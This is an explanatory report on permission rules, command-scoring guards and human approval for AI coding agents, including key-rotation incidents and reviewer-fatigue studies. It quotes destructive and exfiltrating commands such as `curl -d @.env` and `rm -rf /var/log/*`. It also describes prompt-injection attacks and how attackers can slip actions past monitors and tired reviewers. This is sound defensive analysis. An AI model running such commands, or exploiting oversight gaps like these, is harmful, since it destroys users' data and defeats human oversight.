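The owner often can't tell which of these things happened. Rust's *cargo-yank(1)* notes that once a package containing a credential is public, it is impossible to tell whether anyone copied it, and recommends revoking the credential immediately. So a harness shouldn't lower a leak to R2 just because the key can be rotated. R2 requires bounded, knowable consequences, and the consequences of a leak depend on what strangers do before the rotation.

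Some services shorten the time an exposed secret stays usable. PyPI, the main public registry for Python packages, automatically revokes any of its own access tokens that turn up on a public website, according to its *Common questions*. Most keys need manual work. When GitHub searched its own 15,000-plus repositories, it found over 20,000 secrets and took nine months to clear the alerts.

### When rotation causes an outage

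Advice differs on how quickly to revoke a leaked key. GitHub and Rust recommend revoking it immediately, whereas GitGuardian's *What to do if you expose a secret* recommends first finding out what that would break.

Removing an old key too early can cause an outage, as happened at the internet company Cloudflare on March 21, 2025. Its engineers were replacing the credentials that one of its services used to reach stored files. Cloudflare (2025) reports that they omitted the `--env` option from both deployment commands, which sent the new credentials to the default environment instead of production. Believing they had updated production, they removed the old credentials at 20:37. Customers were affected from 21:38. For 1 hour and 7 minutes, all writes and about 35% of reads failed, according to Cybersecurity News' *Password Rotation Error*.

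The commands had deployed valid credentials but to the wrong place. The damage appeared an hour after the last step, so an agent that checked the service right after removing the old credentials would probably have reported success.

Keeping the old and new keys valid for a while reduces the risk but can hide a mistake. *Agent Designer Unreachable*, from the software company Maven AGI, describes how one of the company's services missed an update and kept working on its old credential until the next rotation invalidated it. It is safer to check the access logs for any use of the old key before disabling it.

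A bad key rotation is sometimes reversible. In January 2026, the sign-in provider Logto had an outage of about an hour after changing the key it uses to sign login tokens. Logto's *Postmortem* (2026) states that the company restored service by clearing a cache and going back to the previous key. A month later, Atlassian's Statuspage mistakenly disabled new API keys while cleaning up old ones, then restored them from a database backup (Atlassian Statuspage, *Statuspage API Access Issues*, 2026). Each company could reinstate its keys because it ran the service that checked them. A developer who deletes a key to someone else's service usually can't, and if the key has leaked, reinstating it would restore access for anyone who has a copy.

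An agent can safely prepare a key rotation by creating the new key and listing the programs that use the old one. A person should decide whether to disable a live key, because disabling it could cause an outage and leaving it active prolongs the exposure.

### Withdrawing a published package

A developer who publishes a package by mistake can sometimes remove it, depending on the package registry:

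| Registry | When the publisher can delete | What happens afterward |
|---|---|---|
| npm (JavaScript) | Within 72 hours if no other public package depends on it; later only if it also has one owner and had fewer than 300 downloads in the past week | Nobody can use that version number again or undo the removal |
| PyPI (Python) | At any time | Nobody can upload the deleted files again |
| crates.io (Rust) | The whole package within 72 hours; later only with one owner, fewer than 500 downloads per month of its existence and no dependents | Single versions stay available and can only be hidden |
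| Maven Central (Java) | Never | The publisher can release a corrected version |

The crates.io rules (Bieniek, 2025) are newer than the statement in Rust's publishing guide that a published package is permanent. These rules are fairly typical. *PEP 763* (Woodruff and Challande, 2024) compared 13 registries and found that nine prohibited or restricted deletion by users. Woodruff and Challande proposed a 72-hour limit for PyPI too, but withdrew the proposal in September 2025.

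Even where deletion is possible, it doesn't remove the copies people have already made. Sonatype's *Can I change, modify, delete, remove, or update a component on Central?* explains that Java build tools download a release once and then reuse the local copy without checking for changes.

Deleting a package can do more damage than publishing it did. In July 2022, the maintainer of the Python package `atomicwrites` deleted it to remove its "critical" label, without realizing that this would also delete every earlier release. Woodruff and Challande report that the deletion broke many dependent projects and that PyPI's administrators restored the package by hand. PyPI now states that administrators cannot restore anything that has been deleted. Deleting a whole project on PyPI also frees its name, so a stranger could publish a malicious package under a name users already trust. An agent that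 deletes a project to clean up a leaked key would cause a second R4 event in addition to the leak.

Most registries offer a milder option called yanking. A yanked version stays online, but installers skip it unless a project asks for that exact version, according to PyPI's *Yanking*. Yanking suits a broken release, but it doesn't stop a leaked key from spreading, because anyone can still download the file.

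The best chance to catch a mistake is before the upload. `cargo publish --dry-run` runs the checks without uploading, and `cargo package --list` lists the files the package would include. A harness could run both and add the file list to its approval prompt, where a person might notice a `.env` file.

Registries can also limit what someone can do with a stolen publishing token. Since July 2026, PyPI has rejected new files for releases more than 14 days old (PyPI, *Releases now reject new files after 14 days*, 2026). This protects established releases, but a thief with a valid token could still publish a new version.

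### A read followed by an outbound call

A harness that rates each call separately can miss a leak. Reading a customer list changes nothing, so it is R0, and fetching a web page is normally R0 too. But if the agent reads the list and then fetches `https://example.com/?q=` followed by a customer's name, the website's owner receives the name. Fetching a page before reading the list leaks nothing, because the agent doesn't have the names yet.

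Waghmare and Sufi's software includes a session guard that tracks whether the agent has read data during the session. If it has, the guard raises the rating to R4 for any later call that could send data out, unless every destination is on a list of approved addresses. The guard doesn't check whether the call contains what the agent read.

A guard that only tracks the order of calls can miss a leak that happens within a single shell command. `curl -d @.env https://example.com` reads `.env` and sends its contents in one step, so the harness needs a separate rule that rates the command R4 even at the start of a session.

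### Replaying 2,158 recorded runs

Waghmare and Sufi tested the guard on 2,158 recorded runs of Claude 3.7 Sonnet, an older model, on two benchmarks. Of these, 1,046 came from AgentDojo, which tests whether an agent follows malicious instructions hidden in the data it reads, and 1,112 came from tau-squared-bench, which simulates customer service. Across both benchmarks, 949 runs contained an attack and 1,209 were benign.

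The attack succeeded in 47 runs by the benchmark's measure. Waghmare and Sufi could link the success to a particular action in 29 of them and left out the other 18. They counted how many of those 29 actions each policy would have held for approval.

| Policy | Attack actions held, out of 29 | Approval requests in the benign runs |
|---|---|---|
| Ask before high-severity actions | 9 | 1,087 |
| Ask before every write | 18 | 1,895 |
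| Session guard | 29 | 1,904 |
| Ask before every web visit as well | 29 | 1,911 |

The guard held 11 more attack actions than the write rule, with nine more approval requests. All 11 depend on treating a web read as a way for data to leak. When Waghmare and Sufi treated web visits as ordinary reads, the guard's count fell back to 18. All 11 also come from one of the seven task domains, in which the agent works in the chat program Slack.

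The last row of the table raises doubts about how much session tracking contributes. An earlier version of the mapping rated every web visit R4, whatever the agent had read before. It held the same 29 actions and produced only seven more prompts in the benign runs. Most of the benefit in this test therefore came from rating web visits R4, and very little came from session tracking.

The overall increase of nine requests came entirely from the 97 benign AgentDojo runs, where requests rose 12%, from 76 under the write rule to 85 under the guard. In the Slack runs among them, requests rose from 34 to 47. In the other 1,112 benign runs, all customer service, the guard asked exactly as often as the write rule. Both policies would interrupt people often. Under the guard, only 119 of the 770 benign runs that originally succeeded would have finished without a request.

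Waghmare and Sufi did not rerun any agent. The replay keeps counting calls after the point where a person might have refused one, so it doesn't show whether people would have stopped the attacks or whether the agents would have found another route. It also relies on the researchers' own classification of the benchmarks' 106 tools.

None of the seven domains involves software development, where the guard would probably prompt for approval far more often. A coding agent reads files in almost every session, so the guard would then raise nearly every network call to R4, including a routine `npm install`. Developers would have to put the addresses they use most on an approved list, and some of those can also receive leaked data. If GitHub is on the list, for example, the guard would not flag a push that puts a key in a public repository.

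## Rules that match the text of a command

Permission rules let developers decide in advance what an agent may run. For example, a developer who has classified the common Git commands might allow `git status` (R0), require approval for `git reset` and block `git push --force`. The harness checks each command the model proposes against these rules before running it. This is fast and gives the same answer every time, but the harness decides from the wording of the command and has little information about the files or services the command will change.

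### Splitting, matching and resolving conflicts

Suppose an agent in Claude Code proposes `git status && npm test && git push`. The developer has written an allow rule, `Bash(npm test *)`, and an ask rule, `Bash(git push *)`, where Bash is the name of the shell tool. Claude Code splits the command at each `&&` and checks the three parts separately. It recognizes `git status` as read-only, and `npm test` matches the allow rule, but `git push` matches the ask rule, so Claude Code asks the developer to approve the whole command. According to Anthropic, an ask or deny rule applies if any part of a compound command matches it, and the command runs without a prompt only if every part qualifies.

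The `*` in a rule stands for any text, so its position determines which commands the rule covers. `Bash(git log *)` covers only `git log`, while `Bash(git *)` covers every Git command, including the ones that destroy work. `Bash(ls*)` also matches `lsof`, an unrelated program, but adding a space, as in `Bash(ls *)`, prevents this. Before matching, Claude Code removes certain prefixes that only affect how a command runs, so the rule for `npm test` also covers `timeout 30 npm test`.

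Codex matches whole words from the start of the command, so the pattern `["gh", "pr", "view"]` in OpenAI's *Rules* matches any command that begins with `gh pr view`. Rule writers can list commands that a rule should and should not match, and Codex tests these examples when it loads the rule. This practice is worth copying because a misplaced wildcard is easy to overlook.

Codex and Claude Code treat complicated commands differently. Codex splits a script into separate commands only if it consists of plain words joined by simple operators. Because `npm test > results.txt` redirects output to a file, Codex treats it as a single call to the shell, and an allow rule for `npm test` doesn't apply. Claude Code still matches the rule but separately checks whether the agent may write to `results.txt`. If Claude Code can't parse a command, or the command is longer than 10,000 characters, it doesn't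 treat the command as read-only, and in manual mode it asks the user.

When rules conflict, both harnesses apply the strictest. In Claude Code, a deny rule for `Bash(aws *)` blocks `aws s3 ls` even if a narrower rule allows exactly that command. A developer therefore can't deny every use of a program and then list exceptions, but has to allow the safe forms and leave the others without a rule, so that the harness applies its default. Gemini CLI, Google's command-line agent, gives each rule a numeric priority. An example rule in Google's *Policy engine* denies commands starting with `rm -rf`.

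### Built-in rules and unknown commands

Harnesses also have built-in rules. Zhong and colleagues counted the ones for shell commands and recorded how users can add to them. The table combines their findings with the harness makers' documentation. The third column mentions regular expressions, which are patterns that can also specify alternatives and repetition.

| Harness | Built-in rules | Form of users' own rules | Decisions users can set |
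|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | About 150 | Wildcard | Allow, ask, deny |
| Codex | 120 | Prefix | Allow, ask, deny |
| Gemini CLI | 75 | Prefix or regular expression | Allow, ask, deny |
| Cursor | None | Prefix, with an optional wildcard for arguments | Allow; also deny in the command-line version |
| VS Code Copilot | 122 | Regular expression | Allow, deny |

The number of rules in a harness is a poor measure of how well it protects the user, because one broad rule can cover as many commands as twenty narrow ones. How the harness handles a command that no rule matches probably matters more.

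In manual mode, Claude Code asks the user about an unknown command. In auto mode, now the default for interactive sessions, it sends most such commands to a classifier.

Codex normally runs an unknown command without asking, but inside a sandbox that blocks network access and limits writing to the project and temporary folders. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex needs approval to go beyond those limits. The developer's rules therefore mainly determine what may run outside the sandbox. OpenAI (2026) lets its own engineers' agents run `kubectl get`, `kubectl describe` and `kubectl logs` outside the sandbox, which inspect a Kubernetes system without changing it. Under a stricter setting called "untrusted", Codex automatically runs only known read operations and asks before running anything else.

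Cursor's default mode runs commands on the user's allowlist immediately. It runs other shell commands in a sandbox when they can work there and sends the rest to a classifier, according to Cursor's *Run Modes*. A user who wants a prompt for every command can switch to allowlist mode and leave the list empty.

These defaults lead to different outcomes for the same action. Running an unfamiliar script that overwrites an uncommitted file in the project is R4 if no copy exists. Claude Code's manual mode would ask before running it, but Codex's sandbox permits the write because the file is inside the project.

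### Allowlists and lists of forbidden commands

A team can list the commands an agent may run (an allowlist), or list those it may not run and permit the rest (a denylist). Omissions are riskier in a denylist, because an agent that nobody has forbidden to run `git clean` may delete files that exist nowhere else. Leaving `git diff` off an allowlist just makes the agent interrupt a person unnecessarily.

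Lists of forbidden commands work best when dangerous commands follow familiar patterns. In *CARE*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested a list of 22 regular expressions on 220 dangerous and 329 safe commands. It blocked no safe commands but caught only 38 of the dangerous ones. On a separate collection of published exploit code, which often repeats the same destructive phrases, the list performed better than every other guard they compared.

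An allowlist with overly broad entries can let destructive commands through. One example in Cursor's documentation lists `git`, `npm`, `yarn`, `pnpm`, `cargo` and `make`. Cursor matches by prefix, so `git` covers `git status` but also `git reset --hard` and `git clean -fdx`, which can be R4. It does not cover `gitk`, which is a separate program. Another example, in Cursor's *permissions.json reference*, allows `cargo build` and `cargo test` instead of all of `cargo`, but still includes plain `git`.

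Harness makers have added exceptions for some commands that people are likely to allow too broadly. In Claude Code, `Bash(find *)` doesn't approve a `find` command that deletes files, such as the log-cleaning command described earlier. The developer needs a rule with the command's exact text, such as `Bash(find build -type f -delete)`. Claude Code also doesn't let any allow rule approve a deletion that it detects is aimed at a critical path. Cursor has an optional protection that stops the agent from deleting files automatically, including with `rm`.

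### Why allowing an interpreter allows everything

An interpreter is a program that runs other programs written in a particular language, such as Python or JavaScript. Developers often want an agent to run their Python scripts without asking, so they write the rule `Bash(python:*)`, which is another way of writing `Bash(python *)`. It matches all of these commands:

- `python -c "print(2 + 2)"` prints the number 4.
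- `python -c "open('notes.txt', 'w').write('hello')"` replaces the contents of `notes.txt` with one word.
- `python report.py` does whatever `report.py` contains at that moment, and the agent may have just edited it.

A rule that allows any `python` command permits almost anything the agent could do with the whole shell, because a Python program can read, change or delete any file that the user can, and can send data over the network. The same applies to `node`, which runs JavaScript, and to tools that start another command inside a prepared environment. For example, `Bash(devbox run *)` approves whatever follows `run`. Anthropic recommends naming the inner command as well, as in `Bash(devbox run npm test)`.

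These rules are common. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that in June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had manually created an allow rule for the shell, a share that was growing by roughly five percentage points every five weeks. It adds that 5% allowed any shell command and another 43% had interpreter rules, but it is unclear whether these are percentages of all active users or only of those with rules. If they are percentages of all active users, nearly everyone who wrote a rule had effectively allowed everything. Otherwise, about 24% of active users had done so.

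Anthropic published these figures to support replacing prompts with a classifier, and it doesn't report how many of the rules led to harm. Some of these users may run Claude Code inside a container, where a broad rule does little damage. Even on the lower reading, a harness designer can't assume that a prompt will appear because the default settings require one. Claude Code's auto mode suspends allow rules this broad so that the commands still reach the classifier, and restores the rules when the user switches modes.

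### How CARE scores a command

CARE (Canonicalization, Attribution, and Resolution Engine) combines several clues in a command's text into a score, whereas a pattern either matches or doesn't. Researchers in China, Australia and the United States released it in July 2026. It checks one command at a time, without seeing the user's request or the conversation.

CARE begins by rewriting the command into a standard form, removing outer wrappers and unusual quoting without running anything. It then parses the result into a tree that separates program names, arguments, redirections and operators. If parsing fails and the text contains high-risk words, CARE refuses the command. Otherwise it gives the command four scores between 0 and 1:

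| Evidence | Weight | Examples |
|---|---|---|
| Risk class of the command's name | 0.3 | 0 for reading (`cat`), 0.15 for local writing (`mv`), 0.35 for an unknown name, 0.40 for network transfers (`rsync`), 1.00 for destruction (`mkfs`) |
| Sensitivity of the path | 0.3 | 0 for the project folder, 0.10 for reading a system folder, 0.70 for writing to one, at least 0.85 for any access to login keys |
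| Known dangerous pattern | 0.3 | The confidence in the matching rule, multiplied by 1.00, 0.85 or 0.60 depending on where the rule came from |
| Structure | 0.1 | 0.05 for an ordinary pipe between programs, 1.00 for piping text into an interpreter |

The list of command names has about 250 entries. Certain arguments raise a command's class score. For example, `chmod`, which changes a file's permissions, gets a higher score when it opens a file to everyone. Of the 139 rules in the pattern bank, 92 come from MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalog of attackers' techniques, and 31 come from GTFOBins, a catalog of ordinary Unix programs that attackers misuse. The researchers wrote the other 16 and gave them the lowest weight.

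The total is:

score = 0.3 × class + 0.3 × path + 0.3 × pattern + 0.1 × structure

CARE allows commands that score below 0.15 and refuses those that score 0.35 or more. Commands in between get a warning, which CARE has to resolve before they can run.

The command `cat /etc/os-release` prints the version of Linux. `cat` only reads, so its class score is 0. Reading a file in a system folder adds a path score of 0.10. The command matches no pattern and its structure is plain, so the total is 0.3 × 0.10 = 0.03, and the command runs.

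`rm -rf /var/log/*` deletes the system's logs. In an example in the paper, this deletion gets 0.95 for its class, 1.00 for its path and 1.00 for a matching pattern. Written plainly, the command has a structure score of 0, so its total is 0.285 + 0.300 + 0.300 = 0.885 and CARE refuses it. The paper's version is disguised, which raises the structure score and brings the total to 0.975. The paper's table lists a path score of 0.70, not 1.00, for writing to `/var/log`, but using 0.70 would still give the plain command a total of 0.795.

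A harmless command can get a mid-range score. `rsync -avz ./build/ admin@gpu01:/data/`, which copies a finished build to another machine, scores 0.40 as a network transfer and 0.75 for matching a pattern for transfers between machines, giving a combined score of 0.345.

With these weights, no single kind of evidence can reach the threshold for refusal, because even a score of 1.00 adds at most 0.30. CARE therefore has three checks that turn a warning into a refusal: a strong match with a catalog rule, a high score in a high-risk class, or access to a protected path or secret. If none applies, a language model decides, with instructions to approve only a "routine, reversible" action and to refuse if uncertain. CARE considers reversibility directly only at this step. The model receives the command and its scores but no information about backups, and it approved the `rsync` command.

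### What the CARE tests found

Liu and colleagues compared CARE with other guards on the 549 commands mentioned above. F1 is the harmonic mean of the share of dangerous commands that a guard catches and the share of its refusals that are correct, so a guard scores high only if both are high.

| Guard | Miss rate | False-block rate | F1 | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 22 regular expressions | 82.7% | 0% | 29.5% | 0.01 ms |
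| A general language model judging every command | 32.7% | 11.3% | 73.1% | 45.9 ms |
| Granite Guardian, IBM's safety model | 17.7% | 45.9% | 65.6% | 17.3 ms |
| CARE without its language model | 24.1% | 1.8% | 85.0% | 0.34 ms |
| Full CARE | 24.1% | 0.9% | 85.6% | 2.32 ms |

CARE interrupts safe work far less often than the two language-model guards but still misses 53 of the 220 dangerous commands. Its own language model made little difference. The fixed checks settled 94 of the 117 commands with a warning, and the model handled the other 23. It approved three, all harmless `rsync` commands, and that gain is too small to be statistically significant.

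The low false-block rate also depends on the mix of commands. On three other samples of safe commands, which included some that only looked dangerous, full CARE blocked between 8% and 13%. Even with a false-block rate of 0.9%, CARE could block more safe commands than dangerous ones in ordinary use. Liu and colleagues calculate that if 100 out of 10,000 commands were dangerous, CARE would block about 76 of them and about 90 safe ones.

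CARE's treatment of unknown commands probably explains many of the misses. A command with an unfamiliar name and no other warning signs scores 0.3 × 0.35 = 0.105, so CARE allows it, whereas Waghmare and Sufi would rate it R4. In the version without a language model, Liu and colleagues lowered the first threshold from 0.15 to 0.10, just below that score. The miss rate fell from 24.1% to 3.2%, but the false-block rate rose from 1.8% to 23.1%. The choice of threshold therefore largely determines whether CARE allows unknown commands by default.

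They also ran 600 commands that a language model had written from prompts describing attacks. Each ran in a Docker container, which isolates a program from the rest of the machine. With no guard, 74.8% ran successfully. Full CARE reduced this to 52.5%, but CARE without its language model reduced it to 37.3%.

Adding the language model therefore let through about 91 more of these commands, even though it had helped slightly in the main test. Liu and colleagues plausibly suggest that this happened because the same model, Qwen3-Coder-30B, wrote the commands and judged the doubtful ones, but they did not test a judge from another model family. The harm figure counts commands that a guard allowed and that ran successfully, not the damage they did, so it is more useful for comparing guards than for estimating losses.

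### What the text leaves out

`mv draft.txt notes.txt` replaces `notes.txt` with the draft. Like the earlier edit to `settings.yaml`, it can be R1 or R4, depending on whether a copy of the old `notes.txt` exists. If both files are in the project and no pattern matches, CARE would give the command 0.3 × 0.15 = 0.045 whether or not there is a copy.

The text of other commands, such as `npm test` and `make clean`, doesn't show their effects, which are defined in a file. Claude Code's manual mode partly accounts for this with Git, which can run small programs stored in a repository. It normally runs `git status` without approval, but prompts the user if the same command first changes to another folder, because that folder may contain such programs.

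Zhong and colleagues found rules that did not account for a command's effects contributed to 52 of the 290 public reports they studied (18%). In some, the rules blocked one way of deleting a file but allowed other commands with the same effect. In others, an allowed command did something its approver had not expected. Agents and attackers can also get around text rules, so Anthropic recommends using a sandbox to enforce file and network limits that must hold however a command is worded.

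Tightening the rules can also cause problems when they block work the user wants done. Zhong and colleagues attribute 130 reports at least partly to fixed policies that were too loose for one task or too strict for another. In one report, a Cursor user turned off deletion protection so the agent could clean up duplicate files, and the agent later deleted 90% of the project.

### Hooks that check more than the text

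A hook can supply some of the information missing from a command's text. In Claude Code, a hook that runs before a tool call receives the full command and can refuse it, require a prompt or approve it. Because the hook is an ordinary program, it can also look at the developer's files. A hook for `git reset --hard` could run `git status` first, allow the reset if there are no uncommitted changes, and ask the developer otherwise, while a text rule would have to treat both cases the same way.

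Developers can write these hooks themselves or install existing ones. Destructive Command Guard, an open-source hook for coding agents, blocks commands such as `git reset --hard` and `rm -rf` before they run.

Even when a hook approves a command, Claude Code still refuses it if it matches one of the user's deny rules, and still prompts if it matches an ask rule. The exception is mods, extensions that can answer permission checks after the hooks have run. On a computer without centrally managed settings or a Team or Enterprise login, a mod can approve a command that a deny rule refuses or a hook has blocked. Developers who rely on deny rules should therefore check whether any installed mod overrides them.

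## Asking a person to confirm

When a permission rule or hook results in "ask", the harness stops and a person decides whether to run the command. This protects the developer only if that person can tell what the command will do and still reads the prompt after approving dozens of others.

### What a reviewer needs to know

A confirmation prompt typically shows the command, a short description and a menu of answers. To judge the request, a reviewer needs four facts:

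- the exact target, such as which database, and whether it is the live one or a test copy
- the effect, such as how many files or rows will change
- whether someone can undo it, and for how long
- who else it affects, such as customers or colleagues

Suppose an agent asks to run `python3 setup.py`, a common way to install a Python project. The prompt names a script but gives none of the four facts. As Zhong and colleagues point out, approving the command authorizes whatever code the script contains, as with the `cargo build` prompt described earlier. To know what that code does, the reviewer would have to read the script and everything it loads.

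A longer command can be just as hard to judge. In another of their examples, a user asks Codex to replace one word in a file. The approval prompt shows a script that checks that the file exists, edits it with `sed -i` and then searches for the old and new words, but it doesn't show the line before and after the edit. The user can choose to approve the script and stop being asked about `sed -i`, although a later in-place edit could be R4 if no copy of the file exists.

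The person confirming also needs to know what the command will affect. Alexey Grigorev approved `terraform destroy` believing it would remove only duplicates. A prompt listing the live database among the resources to delete, and showing that deletion protection was off, would have given him a reason to stop.

### How often people approve

According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, users accepted 93% of permission prompts. In August 2026, Anthropic put the figure at 97%. By contrast, users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented for approval.

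A high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness. If 97 of every 100 proposed commands are harmless, a careful reviewer approves 97. Users may also reject a plan because they prefer a different design rather than because they see a danger. Still, the gap suggests that people object more readily when asked about something they can judge.

Many users avoid the prompts. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in the mode that bypasses permission checks, and 62% of users have either used that mode or chosen "don't ask again" for a shell command. The 62% combines two quite different choices, since "don't ask again" silences prompts for only one command.

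Researchers call the loss of attention from repeated prompts approval fatigue. *Habituation at the Gate* (2026) found something similar among people who review pull requests (proposed code changes) written by agents. Among reviewers whose approval rate moved by at least five percentage points, 65% came to approve more often and 35% less often. The paper's analysis of how much effort reviewers put into their comments favors habituation over well-founded trust as the explanation.

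### The experiment with 1,053 testers

Approval rates can't show how many dangerous commands people miss, because nobody knows how many of the approved commands were dangerous. Anthropic therefore ran a controlled experiment. It hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor to work in an environment built for the study. The testers knew that they were in a coding study and that someone was evaluating them, but not which behavior.

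Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, and the vendor recorded the tester's answer. Approving the prompt did no harm because only the text had changed. Anthropic then gave the same commands to the classifier behind Claude Code's auto mode.

The testers refused 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6%), while the classifier blocked 937 (89%). The published totals are enough to fill in the whole comparison:

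| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

Requiring both the tester and the classifier to approve would have stopped 943 commands, only six more than the classifier stopped alone. Testers also refused fewer of the dangerous commands as sessions went on, from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed flat.

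Anthropic was testing its own product. It doesn't report how many harmless commands the classifier or the testers refused in the experiment, and a classifier that blocked everything would have scored 100%.

The testers also had little to lose, since they didn't own the code and could reasonably assume that a test environment contained nothing valuable. A developer reviewing a command that would run on their own database might be more careful. But the testers knew they were being evaluated, which could have made them more careful than usual.

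Each tester saw only one dangerous prompt, so the fall from 17% to 5% is a difference between groups of testers. Those who got through more than 50 prompts may have been quicker to click from the start. The design also can't show whether a person who catches one dangerous command reads later prompts more closely. Even so, most testers approved commands that Anthropic describes as clearly dangerous, and only a very large ownership effect would turn 13.6% into reliable protection.

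Anthropic also looked at real users, who did own their work. It had a model grade the harm in sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. The agent did serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This is weaker evidence than the experiment because users chose their own mode, and those who choose manual approval may be working on riskier systems.

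### A model in which asking more often lowers safety

If attention declines with every prompt, a harness that asks about a harmless command makes the reviewer less likely to catch a dangerous one later. Turan (2026), in *Oversight Has a Capacity*, turned this into a formula. The chance that a reviewer catches a dangerous action at request number *n* is:

*r*(*n*) = max(0.2, 1 − 0.02 × max(0, *n* − *C*))

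*C* is the reviewer's capacity, the number of requests they can review before tiring. With a capacity of 25, the reviewer catches all dangerous actions up to the 25th request, half at the 50th, and 20% from the 65th onward.

Suppose an agent proposes 100 actions, ten of them dangerous, and the reviewer has a capacity of 25 requests. The harness can ask the reviewer to confirm 10, 40 or all 100 of the actions. The harness identifies dangerous actions imperfectly, and the dangerous actions are evenly spaced among the requests.

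| Requests | Dangerous actions among them | Dangerous actions run without asking | Expected number approved by mistake | Total that get through |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 4 | 6 | 0 | 6 |
| 40 | 8 | 2 | 0.6 | 2.6 |
| 100 | 10 | 0 | 4.8 | 4.8 |

Asking about everything is better than asking about ten actions but worse than asking about 40. Turan found the same pattern in a simulation with 125 coding-agent actions, chosen to be hard to judge and scored for risk by a language model. With a capacity of 25, 57% of the dangerous actions got through when the harness asked about all 125. At the best setting, the harness asked about 64% of the actions, and 42% of the dangerous ones got through.

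An attacker could exploit the effect by burying one malicious action among routine ones. In the simulation, a harness that asked for confirmation of 88% of routine actions let the malicious one through 40% of the time after 50 routine actions. A harness that asked for confirmation of 26% caught it every time until there were about 100 routine actions.

These results all come from modelling rather than a human study. Turan chose the slope and floor of the curve instead of measuring them, and states that the result follows directly from assuming that reviewers tire.

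Anthropic's experiment supports the assumption that performance declines, but its reviewers started with a catch rate of about 17% instead of 100%, which changes the conclusion. If the catch rate in the small example falls in a straight line from 17% to 5% over the first 50 requests and then stays there, 9.1 dangerous actions get through with 40 requests and 9.3 with 100. The number of prompts hardly matters for such reviewers, because they miss nearly all the dangerous actions either way. Reducing prompts helps most when people will read and can understand the requests that remain.

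### Which requests developers read

*Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) interviewed 18 practitioners and then surveyed 115, of whom 107 answered the questions about permissions. About 48% said they read permission requests carefully, 34% said they skim them and 21% said they approve by default. A third said they had become less careful over time.

About 77% of respondents look more closely at writes, deletions and requests for higher privileges, and 64% at anything unexpected. Sixty-two percent would never give an agent access to sensitive data, 56% would never grant it administrator rights, and 23% would never let it delete files. Interviewees also considered whether they could undo an action. Salerno and colleagues recommend that prompts state whether an action can be rolled back and how.

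Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers and found that 64% often approved at least one of seven types of action without close review. The share ranged from 21% for reading secrets and other sensitive files to 36% for using the internet and outside services. Among developers who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, 61% still often approved at least one type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the others, a difference that was not statistically significant.

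Developers who knew about the risks weren't more careful either. Of those who knew of a security or privacy problem involving agents, 70% often approved something without close review, compared with 43% of those who didn't. Heavy users may both hear about more problems and approve more requests, but the difference remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how much and how long people had used agents.

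Developers who inspected diffs, which show line by line what changed, were less likely to approve destructive commands and changes to production settings without careful review. Wu and colleagues suggest that a diff gives people something concrete to check.

Both surveys rely on self-reports, and people probably overstate how careful they are. Neither survey shows how often an unread request turned out to be dangerous.

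### Letting users write the rules in advance

Another way to reduce prompts is to have users set permissions for whole categories of action beforehand. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested this with 113 people who don't work in software. Each supervised an assistant through the same simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which exceeded the user's request, such as reading private messages or buying a lounge pass.

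One group approved every action. A second group decided on only the ten actions that a model referred to them, including all seven unrequested ones. The third group first wrote a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing, deleting, and reading private information.

| Group | Average prompts per person | Unrequested actions blocked | Unrequested actions approved when asked |
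|---|---|---|---|
| Approved every action | 18.0 | 60% | 40% |
| Model referred some actions | 10.0 | 54% | 46% |
| Wrote their own rules | 10.9 | 40% | 67% |

The people who wrote rules blocked the least. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which left most decisions until the agent was about to act, and then they usually approved. Of the 148 unrequested actions that ran in this group, a person approved 133, and 15 ran automatically under an "allow" rule. The difference from the group that approved everything is statistically significant, but the difference from the model-assisted group is not significant after correction for multiple comparisons. Yan's study doesn't establish why writing rules was associated with more approvals.

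The group with the most prompts blocked the most. This doesn't contradict Turan's model, which predicts no fatigue in a session of 18 prompts because that is below the capacity of 25 used above. Yan's participants also saw plain descriptions of the data, recipient or amount involved, rather than shell commands. They weren't developers and risked nothing real, so their blocking rates can't be applied to coding agents.

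### Prompts that show consequences

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) tested how much the content of a confirmation prompt matters. In its example, a user tells an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor. Instructions hidden in a supplier's note lead the agent to copy the raw invoices into `report.csv` and then ask to send that file to the auditor. The recipient is approved and the filename looks ordinary, so a reviewer who sees only the final request has no reason to refuse.

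Hossain and colleagues showed each of 80 volunteers one of four approval screens. The first gave a short description of the action, and the second added its exact details. The third added the user's original instructions and a log of everything the agent had done. The fourth linked the same facts into a statement of the consequence, such as that the attachment came from raw invoice rows and sending it would transfer those rows to the auditor. The reviewer still had to decide whether that broke the rules. Each person judged six safe and six unsafe requests, for 960 decisions in total.

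| Screen | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact details | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Details, instructions and log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| Same facts, with the consequence stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. The further gain from stating the consequence was 7.9 percentage points after adjustment, but this is uncertain because the 95% interval runs from a 19.7-point reduction to a 3.8-point increase. Stating the consequence also didn't help when the violation depended on a chain of earlier steps. In those cases, people approved 7 of 30 unsafe requests with each of the last two screens.

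Half of the requests in the study were unsafe, so participants had good reason to stay alert, whereas a developer might see one dangerous request in several hundred. The better screens also took about twice as long to read as the short description. At 33 seconds each, 50 prompts would take almost 28 minutes, so detailed prompts are practical only if the harness shows few of them.

### Which actions justify an interruption

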